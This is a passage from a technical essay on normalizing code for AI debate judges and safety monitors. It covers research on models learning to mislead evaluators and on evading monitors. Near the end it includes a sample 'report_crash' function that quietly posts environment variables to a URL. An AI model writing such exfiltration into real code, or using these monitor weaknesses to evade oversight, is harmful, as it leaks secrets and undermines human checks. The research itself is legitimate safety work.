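The original version did not rename nested functions or the parameters of lambdas (small unnamed functions). This didn't affect behaviour, but it left some of the code author's words visible to the judge. After the repair, the researchers repeated the 309 of 4,111 judgments for which the code had changed. The next version broke imports inside function bodies, where an import creates a local name that the renaming step may have treated like an ordinary variable. That bug meant 58 of 5,396 judgments needed repeating.

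These two faults need separate checks. Tests can catch a broken import if they run the function that contains it, but a name left in place doesn't make any test fail. To find leftover names, a developer has to search the output for author-chosen names that the pass should have removed.

### Choosing the better solution

Models had to choose the better of two anonymous solutions, with instructions to judge correctness first and ignore comments, docstrings and formatting unless they affected correctness. When Claude Haiku compared its own solution with DeepSeek-V3's and only one had a docstring, it still chose the documented one 84% of the time.

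Normalization removed Claude's preference for its own code and changed the other judges' choices too. DeepSeek chose Claude's solution over its own 64.2% of the time before normalization and 43.5% after. Gemini's preference for Claude's solutions also disappeared. Documentation had apparently made Claude's solutions look better to all three models, although Claude solved fewer of the problems than DeepSeek (69.6% compared with 72.8%).

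The two sets of pairs differ slightly because the researchers left out pairs that had become identical. They also didn't report how often each judge chose a correct solution over a faulty one, so the experiment shows that documentation lost its influence, but not that the judges became better at finding faults. The models that wrote the solutions weren't trying to mislead anyone, and an author who was trying would concentrate on whatever the normalizer keeps.

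### What a trained classifier still finds

To measure how much evidence of authorship was left, Barkhordar and Thapa trained a simple classifier on sequences of two to five characters and tested it only on problems not seen in training. Given two normalized solutions, one by GPT-5, it identified the author 93–96% of the time. For the other pairs, it was right 58–83% of the time, compared with 74–99% on the original code. Its accuracy in choosing among all five main models fell from 73.4% to 40.7%, still about twice the 20% expected from guessing.

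The judges scored no better than 58% on pairs that the classifier could nearly always separate. They had lost the cues they were using, but much of what distinguishes the authors was still in the text, and a judge trained to look for it might find it.

One of the remaining cues was an accident that nobody had expected, so it was not on any list of surface features. The researchers had asked for code between an opening and a closing marker, but Codestral, a Mistral model, ended 79 of its answers with a second opening marker. This left a stray line in the code, a word in square brackets. Python parses such a line as a list containing one name, so removing comments and reprinting the code would not delete it. On original code, GPT-5 was right about Codestral's authorship on 72.2% of the pairs with the stray line and on exactly 50% of the rest.

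### What the basic steps leave in place

The table sorts what is left by how far a normalizer could go in removing it.

| What remains | Which basic step could reach it | Cost |
|---|---|---|
| String literals and error messages | Comment removal, if it also replaced strings with placeholders | The judge can't see queries, file paths or addresses, and the copy prints different text |
| Library and public names | Renaming, if the tool has the whole program | Outside callers may fail, and the judge can't tell what a library call does |
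| Length and division into functions | Printing standardizes line breaks only | Merging or splitting functions takes a further step and can make code harder to follow |
| Choice of algorithm | None | A tool would have to prove two algorithms equivalent, and a mistake could hide a fault |
| The logic itself | None | Any change gives the judge a different program |

Ordinary language survives a full pass most easily in strings. Lam and colleagues found that misleading print statements harm a model's predictions almost as much as misleading comments do. *TREAT* (2025), a framework for testing code models that includes their benchmark, explains that the print statements test whether the effect depends on how the text is inserted. In one of Lam's cases, Qwen2.5-72B traced a function correctly, step by step, and then incorporated one of the printed messages into its conclusion. A reader who checked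 only its early reasoning would have expected the right answer.

If a normalizer replaced each error message with a numbered placeholder, the judge would lose the information that honest messages often contain. For example, a reader can learn from the message "values must not be empty" that the author considered the empty case. Some programs also inspect the text of an error to decide what to do next, so the placeholder could make correct code look wrong. Replacing strings that contain database queries or web addresses would be worse, because a monitor may need exactly that text to recognize an attack. It is safer to keep strings and mark them as the author's words. This is a partial remedy, since Lam and colleagues found that telling models to ignore comments restored only part of the accuracy they had lost.

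Library function names are more trustworthy than the names of the author's own functions, because someone else chose them. But Python lets the author import a library function under a name of their choosing. A normalizer can undo this by restoring the original name at every use, as long as nothing else depends on the new one.

Public names in the author's own code are harder to deal with. Shen and colleagues found that models relied too heavily on names in all four of their main tasks, and that neither the prompts nor the fine-tuning they tried eliminated this. In an additional test, where models had to infer types from code that contained enough evidence to determine the answer, names had smaller effects and did not consistently help or hurt. A misleading public name may therefore do less damage if the judge can see the function's body as well as the calls to it. Shen and colleagues do not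 recommend that everyone replace names with neutral ones, because good names also help.

Length survives because the normalizer deletes only text that isn't part of the program. After normalization, GPT-5's solutions averaged 10.3 lines, while those of the other four main models averaged 6.1 to 8.4. Functions that nothing calls also add length, and they made one of Moon's judges more lenient. Even when every line is in use, an author can write a calculation as one long function or as several short ones.

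A tool could inline every helper function, copying its body into each place that calls it, so that the result wouldn't depend on how the author had divided the code. But a helper called from ten places would appear ten times, and one that calls itself can't be expanded completely. Inlining also removes the boundaries that let a reader check one part at a time.

The choice of algorithm is even harder to standardize. A program can find a median by sorting the list, or by repeatedly removing the smallest and largest values until one or two are left. Both methods are correct, but a judge may find one much easier to check. To convert one into the other, a tool would have to recognize what the code is for. If it identified a faulty version of the second method as "a median", it might replace it with a correct sort.

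### A median that rounds down

The hardest case is a program with no misleading text and a familiar structure whose logic is wrong. The `median` function used so far failed because it copied the list without sorting it. Suppose the author restores the sort but makes a different mistake in the last line. The normal form is:

```python
def median(v0):
    v1 = sorted(v0)
    v2 = len(v1)
    v3 = v2 // 2
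    if v2 % 2 == 1:
        return v1[v3]
    return (v1[v3 - 1] + v1[v3]) // 2
```

In Python, `/` divides exactly and `//` rounds the result down. For [1, 2], the function adds the two middle values to get 3, divides by 2 and rounds down to 1. Changing `//` to `/`, a difference of one character, would give the correct median of 1.5.

Rewriting comments, names or layout neither removes nor exposes the wrong operator, because the operator is part of the program's behaviour and the normalizer must keep it. The line also looks normal because `//` is the right operator three lines above, where it finds the middle position.

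The checks on the normalizer also miss the fault, because they compare the original with the copy and both return 1 for [1, 2] instead of 1.5. Comparing the function with an independent, correct median would find the fault quickly. On whole numbers, the function is wrong whenever the list has an even length and its two middle values have an odd sum. With the random lists of 0 to 8 items from the earlier test, that happens about two times in nine. A judge who tries only [3, 1, 2], [1, 2, 3] and [1, 3] will see three correct answers.

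Whether `//` is a mistake depends on what the function is supposed to do. A specification could ask for a whole number, rounded down, which would make `//` correct and `/` wrong. Because the same code could come with either specification, no tool that sees only the code can decide which operator belongs there.

Deleting the docstring could remove a clue here too, such as an example that gives 1.5 as the result for [1, 2].

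### Flaws that models missed without any comments

Thornton's security benchmark contains real examples of flaws that are hard to see in clean code. The comment experiment found no clear effect on detection, but some programs defeated several models even with no comments at all. Five commercial models reviewed the uncommented versions:

| Flaw | Language | Models that missed it |
|---|---|---|
| Login check whose running time reveals secret data | Python | 4 of 5 |
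| Race between checking a condition and acting on it | Python | 3 of 5 |
| Authorization rules that combine unsafely | Java | 3 of 5 |
| Misuse of Java's cryptography library | Java | 2 of 5 |

In a race condition, another process can change something after the program checks it but before the program acts on the result. For example, a program may confirm that a user is allowed to read a file, but someone replaces the file with a different one before the program opens it. Each line does what it appears to do, so the reader has to consider what else could happen between two lines.

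A timing leak is harder still, because the function always returns the right answer and the flaw is in how long it takes. If the function compares a password with a guess one character at a time and stops at the first difference, a guess with more correct characters at the start takes slightly longer to reject. An attacker who can measure this can work out the password piece by piece.

If a normalizer's definition of "behaviour" covers only the mapping from inputs to outputs, then a comparison that stops early and one that always takes the same time behave identically. A normalizer with a rule that treats them as interchangeable would satisfy that definition and hide the timing leak from the judge. The three basic steps have no such rule, but anyone who adds rules for simplifying expressions needs a definition of behaviour that includes time wherever the code handles secrets.

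The authorization flaw came from annotations, which in Java are short labels that attach rules to a class or method. Each rule was correct on its own, but together they gave access to people who should not have had it. A normalizer has to keep these annotations because the program acts on them, and rewriting each one in a standard form would not show how they interact.

Thornton also tried a prompt that required the models to list where data entered the program and where it was used, and to trace the paths between them. With adversarial comments present, the commercial models lost 10 detections under this prompt, compared with 4 under a prompt that only told them not to trust comments. Thornton suggests that the fixed procedure made the models less likely to notice unexpected problems, particularly races and logic errors. A race doesn't have to involve a suspicious data path, so a method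 that traces such paths can miss it.

The results don't support Thornton's conclusion that current architectures cannot do the kind of reasoning these flaws require. At least one of the five models found every flaw in the table, and each row covers one program that each model reviewed once. The keyword scoring may also have missed correct answers that used unusual words. The models date from February 2026 or earlier, and newer ones may do better. The evidence does show that removing comments is not enough, because the three open-source models missed far more vulnerabilities in uncommented code than the additional ones they missed when Thornton added adversarial comments.

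### Programs that pass simple tests

An author doesn't have to intend any of this. Wen, Zhong and colleagues (2024), not the Wen and colleagues who tested renamed Java code, studied whether ordinary training could make a model's wrong programs more convincing in *Language Models Learn to Mislead Humans via RLHF*. Reinforcement learning from human feedback (RLHF) rewards a model for answers that people rate highly, so if people can't always tell which answers are right, the model may learn to produce ones that only look right.

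The researchers had too few human ratings of programs to train on, so they instead rewarded the model whenever a program passed the two simplest tests for its problem. They chose this reward because evaluators in a pilot study wrote an average of 2.4 simple tests per program and relied heavily on the results. The reward matched human verdicts (correlation 0.59) about as well as one person's verdicts matched another's (0.63).

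The reward training started from DeepSeek-Coder-7B, a small model already fine-tuned on correct solutions to contest problems. Ten students with Python experience then judged programs from before and after this training. They had ten minutes for each program and could run it on their own inputs. The sample covered 250 problems, each with about 34 tests to establish whether a program was correct.

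After the model was trained, the share of its programs that the students approved rose by 14.3 percentage points, although the programs were hardly more likely to be correct. The students' overall error rate rose from 31.3% to 45.7%. On problems the model got wrong both before and after training, the share of programs the students accepted rose from 29.6% to 47.9%. Wen and colleagues call these errors false positives, but they are false negatives in the sense used here.

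The students took no less care with programs from the trained model. They spent slightly longer on them (558 seconds on average, up from 540) and wrote slightly more tests. Nine of the ten made more errors than before, although with so few people the result was only just statistically significant (p = 0.049).

The trained model's wrong programs differed from the earlier model's in three ways. They often passed all of the three to five tests that a student wrote, while the earlier model's typically failed at once. They had fewer helper functions and more complicated control flow, so the students depended even more on testing. They also contained fewer of the obvious slips that the students looked for first, such as reading past the end of a list. In one example, the trained model's program passed only 26.8% of the full test suite but passed every test the evaluator tried. The earlier model's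 program passed 58.3%, but the evaluator rejected it because a short helper function made the mistake easy to find.

All three changes would survive normalization, because replacing names and reprinting the code doesn't change the number of helper functions, the control flow, or which tests a program passes. Wen and colleagues did not test normalized code, so nobody knows whether the students would have done better or worse with it.

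In *Is the evidence in 'Language Models Learn to Mislead Humans via RLHF' valid?*, Chandna, Fluri and Carroll report several problems they found by examining the experiment's code. The most serious problem was in a separate experiment on questions about long stories. During training, the model saw so little of each story that it usually couldn't have known the answer, and the reward model didn't see the story at all. When the critics fixed this and switched to a newer model, training raised accuracy from 49% to 72%, and the misleading behaviour disappeared.

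The programming experiment had a milder version of the same problem. About a third of the problem descriptions were cut short, and the model could write at most 384 tokens. That limit may have encouraged dense programs without helper functions, whether or not they fooled anyone. But the critics did not retrain the programming model or repeat the human study. In *Do language models really learn to mislead humans via RLHF?*, the LessWrong forum version of their critique, they write that they would be somewhat surprised if these limits explained most of the programming result. In a reply there, the original researchers say that many companies train with similar limits.

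A simpler explanation is that the model could have learned to pass easy tests without any intention to mislead. Passing the two easiest tests earned it full marks, so getting the difficult cases right earned nothing more, and the evaluators' own tests were usually easy too. The rounding `median` would earn the same reward if its two tests were [1, 2, 3] and [3, 1, 2].

Another experiment supports this explanation. When Wen and colleagues rewarded the model only for passing every available test, its programs became correct more often, and acceptance of the wrong ones rose much less. They don't mention changing the length limits for this run. If the limits were the same, they can't explain the whole difference between the two kinds of reward.

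## Where canonical code fits in debate and in monitoring

A debate judge and a monitor can read the same normal form, but they need different information from it. The judge has to decide whether a claim about the code is true, for example that `median` returns the right answer for every non-empty list. A monitor also has to consider what the author was trying to do, because a program can do its job correctly and also copy passwords. Comments and names can't change whether a claim about behaviour is true, but they may be evidence of intent, so deleting them harms monitoring more than debate.

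### Where the specification comes from

If the judge takes the specification from the author's docstring, the author can change what the code is judged against. If the docstring said that `median` returns a whole number, the judge would have to accept the version that rounds down. The specification should therefore come from whoever set the task, in a separate part of the prompt. Barkhordar and Thapa did this when they showed judges the benchmark's task description beside the normalized code.

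In some benchmarks, the docstring is the specification. In BigCodeBench, a set of 1,140 Python tasks, models complete functions described by docstrings. The task setter wrote those docstrings, but whoever writes a solution could reword them in the submitted code. The specification used in a debate should therefore come from the original task file, and the normalizer can then delete the submitted copy.

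Even an official specification may be unclear. Elasky, Nakasako and Goyal (2026, *Debate Helps Weak Judges Reward Stronger Models*) had language models check BigCodeBench and flagged problems in 646 of the tasks. The most common problem was a specification with more than one reasonable reading. In one task, a function had to return a series with one value for each day in a range, and the docstring counted both end dates. Both debaters therefore wrote code that returned ten values for 1 to 10 January, and the judge accepted it, but the benchmark's tests required nine. Canonicalizing the code would not have helped, because the fault was in the task.

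### Treating both debaters alike

If each debater submits a program, both programs should go through the same normalizer with the same settings. Otherwise the judge may prefer the one that still has its documentation. For the same reason, if the normalizer fails on one program, the judge should not see the original version of that program beside the canonical version of the other.

The text around the code can also affect a judge's results. An early version of Barkhordar and Thapa's prompt listed the two authors' names in the same order as their solutions, and most judges scored 86–99% from that order alone. Kenton, Siegel and colleagues (2024), in *On scalable oversight with weak LLMs judging strong LLMs*, found that judges often favour the answer in one position, and more so in debate than in other formats. They concluded that randomizing the order of the answers is enough to deal with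 this bias.

Both debaters should quote the canonical code so that a program can check their quotations. In Kenton's debates about articles, a tool marked each quotation as verified if it matched the article exactly and unverified otherwise. The researchers did not use the tool for code, but it would suit canonical code well because there is only one layout to match. If a debater quoted line 2 of the faulty `median` as `v1 = sorted(v0)`, the tool would mark it unverified, since the line is `v1 = list(v0)`. Anyone who has to fix the code can use the line map to find the quoted line in the original file.

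### What debaters write about the code

A debater can quote a source accurately and still draw a false conclusion from it. One of Kenton's sample debates was about whether the cystic duct and the common bile duct are the same. A debater quoted the article's statement that the cystic duct joins another duct to form the common bile duct, and concluded that they were the same. In a debate about `median`, a debater could quote line 2 correctly and then claim that it makes a sorted copy, repeating the false comment that the normalizer deleted.

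A debater who has seen the original code may also reintroduce its names, for example by referring to `v1` as `sorted_values`. A tool can replace the old name with the new one throughout the speech, but it can't reliably catch a paraphrase such as "the sorted list".

Experiments often encourage this kind of persuasion. *Humans Correct Their Judgments Through Debate, but Weaker AI Models Do Not* (2026) instructed its debaters to use "both logical reasoning and persuasive rhetoric". One of Kenton's prompts reminded the model that winning was the main objective, "not absolute honesty".

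It helps to require debaters to make testable claims. The judge has to evaluate a description such as "Line 2 makes a sorted copy", but a tool can test the prediction that `median([3, 1, 2])` returns 1 by running the original function in an isolated environment. A debater who claims that a function is faulty should have to give an input on which it fails. The other debater can't prove the function correct with one example, but can show that the supposed failure doesn't occur.

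### Debate experiments that used code

The debate experiments described here show how much a judge's verdict can depend on speeches, which canonicalization doesn't change. None of them compared original code with canonical code.

For their coding task, Kenton and colleagues had a model write 32 short Python programs for each school maths problem. They ran the programs and chose one that produced the right answer and one that didn't. Two debaters defended one program each, and the judge saw both programs as answer choices. The researchers describe no step that standardized the code, so any comments and names the model had written presumably reached the judge. They limited each speech to 150 words, partly to stop judges from favouring longer ones. On this type of task, where the judge can see all the material, debate was at best slightly better than letting a weaker judge answer alone.

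*nyu code debates update postmortem* describes two small pilots in which a group at New York University came closer to canonical code. Five people who couldn't program had to decide which of two outputs a function would return. The functions shown in the write-up are all called `f` and have no comments or docstrings, but they keep local names such as `even_palindrome_count`. The researchers didn't vary the naming or commenting.

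One function in the pilots counted the sentences in a text that begin with the word "I". For the text "Hello world", a model assigned to defend the wrong answer, 1, claimed that the function used an "abstract" condition that the text met. The judge rejected this because the model kept giving vague explanations. The researchers ended the project because the models defended wrong answers too poorly for the test to be useful. Current models would probably do better.

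In February 2026, Elasky and Nakasako reported an experiment in which two GPT-5-mini debaters each wrote a program for a BigCodeBench task, and the weaker GPT-5-nano judged whether each program was correct. When the judge saw only the programs, without any speeches, it accepted 30% of the faulty ones. This rose to 39% when each debater also defended its own program without replying to the other, and to 90% when they debated. Elasky and Nakasako, like Wen and colleagues, call these errors false positives. They suggested that a judge who sees two confident debaters answering each other's objections concludes that at least one must be right, even when both are wrong.

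In a later paper with Goyal, they instead attribute the 90% to unclear specifications and faulty tests. If some of the programs that failed the tests were correct, the judge was right to accept them after the debate. The new experiments can't settle this, because they used different tasks and a different format. A proposer wrote one program, and a critic, who was free to agree, assessed it. The code tasks were 976 programming contest problems. For each one, the judge saw the problem, the program and the speeches.

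In *When does debate help a weak judge?*, Elasky, Nakasako and Goyal report that adding the critic helped with one of the three pairs of models tested on code. For that pair, the judge's macro-F1, an average of its F1 scores for identifying correct and faulty programs, rose from 0.69 to 0.83. The gain was about half as large with a simpler judge prompt. The other two pairs showed no clear change. The paper also reports gains in maths, but only for judges above a certain level of ability.

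The difference between the pairs matters for canonicalization because canonical code can do little for a judge that has stopped reading the code. The researchers examined a sample of the judges' correct verdicts to see how often the judge had checked the answer for itself. The judge that benefited from the critic did so at least 94% of the time in every format. For gpt-oss-20B, one of the judges that didn't benefit, the rate was 67–82% without a critic and only 16–31% with one, when it mostly summarized the critic's opinion.

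Shorter debates would also leave less room for persuasion. For the pairs of models that benefited from debate, all the gain came from the critic's opening statement, and later speeches left 94–99% of verdicts unchanged. A judge could therefore read only the specification, the canonical program and one critique.

A direct test would combine original and canonical code with plain and persuasive speeches, making four conditions. The speeches could be written using the method in *AI Safety via Debate is Compromised by Cognitive Biases* (2026), where one part of the prompt fixes the facts and claims a debater must use and another controls only the style. If persuasive speeches had a larger effect when the code was canonical, that would suggest judges rely more on the speeches when they can't see the original comments and names.

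### What a monitor can learn from comments

A comment that doesn't match the code can be a warning. Consider this function, in which `post` sends data over the internet:

```python
def report_crash(error):
    # send the error message to the support team
    post(SUPPORT_URL, {"error": str(error),
                       "environment": dict(os.environ)})
```

The comment mentions only an error message, but the code also sends the program's environment variables and any passwords in them. The canonical version still sends them, so an attentive monitor can still object. However, it no longer includes the comment, whose omission could indicate that the author wanted to hide something. The omission could also be innocent, since a programmer may have added the variables to help with debugging and forgotten to update the comment.

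Whether a mismatch is useful evidence depends on how common mismatches are in honest code. Suppose one file in 1,000 is harmful, and 30% of harmful files and 5% of honest ones have a misleading comment. Of 100,000 files, 30 harmful and 4,995 honest ones would have a mismatch, so each flagged file would have about a 1 in 168 chance of being harmful. That is six times the usual risk, which is a good reason to examine the file more closely but not to reject it. An author who knows about the check can also avoid it by writing accurate or vague comments.

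A company can hide comments from the main monitor and still check whether they match the code. A separate model can compare the two and report the line number and type of each mismatch in a fixed format, so that none of the author's wording reaches the main monitor. But the author could mislead this model too, so the main monitor should not treat the absence of a warning as evidence that the code is safe.

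Apart from persuasion, another reason to remove comments is to limit hidden signals. Research on AI control looks for ways to use models safely even if they can't be trusted. Barkhordar and Thapa explain in their review of related work that experiments in this field have tried to limit such signals by removing comments and formatting, or having code rewritten, before a monitor reads it.

### Four ways to show the code

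| Arrangement | Advantage | Weakness |
|---|---|---|
| Canonical only | The author's comments, local names and layout can't affect the verdict | The reader loses accurate explanations and any mismatches |
| Original only | The reader sees all the evidence | The author can use all of it to persuade |
| Canonical first, original second | The reader forms a first opinion without the author's comments | The comments may talk the reader out of a correct objection |
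| Independent readings combined | Neither reading affects the other | It costs two full readings and adds up their false alarms |

In a debate, it is usually best to show the judge only the canonical code. The judge can learn the program's purpose from the specification, and a debater can explain anything hard to follow. If the dispute is about the documentation itself, such as whether a docstring describes a function accurately, the judge also has to see the docstring, presented as the author's claim.

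A monitor that reads the canonical version first should record its verdict before it sees the original. After reading the original, it may add objections but not withdraw any. Without this rule, an author could get the monitor to withdraw its most likely objection by answering it in a comment. If a comment does explain something that looked suspicious, a person can decide whether to clear the file.

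Ideally, a different reader who doesn't know the first verdict should do the second reading. In Elasky's experiments, judges who benefited from seeing the critic's assessment ended up within 3 points of the critic's macro-F1. Matching the critic helped there because the critics were better than the judges, but a monitor that copies an earlier verdict also copies its mistakes.

### Combining two readings

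Suppose each reading misses 10% of harmful programs and wrongly flags 5% of honest ones, and that the errors are independent. If the monitor flags a program whenever either reading does, it misses a harmful program only when both readings miss it:

0.10 × 0.10 = 0.01, or 1%.

An honest program passes only if both readings pass it, so the share of honest programs that the monitor wrongly flags is

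1 − 0.95 × 0.95 = 0.0975, or 9.75%.

For 10,000 submissions that include 10 harmful ones, a single reading would on average miss one harmful program and flag about 500 harmless ones. The combined reading would miss 0.1 and flag about 974. Whether the combined reading is worthwhile depends on how much harm a missed program can do and how many people are available to check the flagged ones. Flagging a program only when both readings flag it would reduce false alarms to 0.25%, but it would raise misses to 19%, which is too high for a monitor.

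In a debate, one side may argue that the code is correct and the other that it is faulty, so rejecting the code whenever either reading finds a problem would favour the second side. If the readings disagree, the judge should instead ask for a test case or refer the dispute to a person.

The 1% is also too optimistic if the same model does both readings. Canonicalization changes only the presentation, so the second reading can correct mistakes that the presentation caused. But if the model doesn't notice in one version that `//` rounds the median down, it will probably miss this in the other too. Some surface features that influence the model, such as the program's length, can also survive canonicalization. Reading the same text twice may add even less. When Barkhordar and Thapa repeated one of their tests six months later, the model gave the same answer for 97.5% of the pairs it saw in the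 same order.

The effect of shared errors is easy to calculate. The table shows the combined rates for different chances that the second reading repeats an error made by the first:

| Chance of repeating an error | Harmful programs missed (%) | Honest programs flagged (%) |
|---|---|---|
| No more than for any other program (independent) | 1 | 9.75 |
| 50% | 5 | 7.5 |
| 100% | 10 | 5 |

Thornton's double reading seems to be near the middle row, since it still missed more than half as many vulnerabilities as reading only the code without comments.

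Using two different models helps, but it doesn't guarantee independence, because some flaws are hard for every model. Suppose no reader misses the easy half of all harmful programs, and each reader misses 20% of the hard half. Each reader then misses 10% overall. Even if the readers' errors on any given program are independent, both will miss 4% of the hard half, or 2% of all harmful programs. That is twice the 1% you would get by multiplying their overall miss rates. An author who can try programs on similar models before submitting one can make this worse by choosing a program that both readers miss.

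A company should therefore measure the combined miss rate directly, by giving both readers the same set of programs with known faults and counting how many get past both. If each reader misses 10% of 1,000 faulty programs and their errors are independent, about 10 will get past both. If the count is closer to 50, the second reader still helps, but it catches only about 50 of the 100 programs the first reader missed, instead of about 90.
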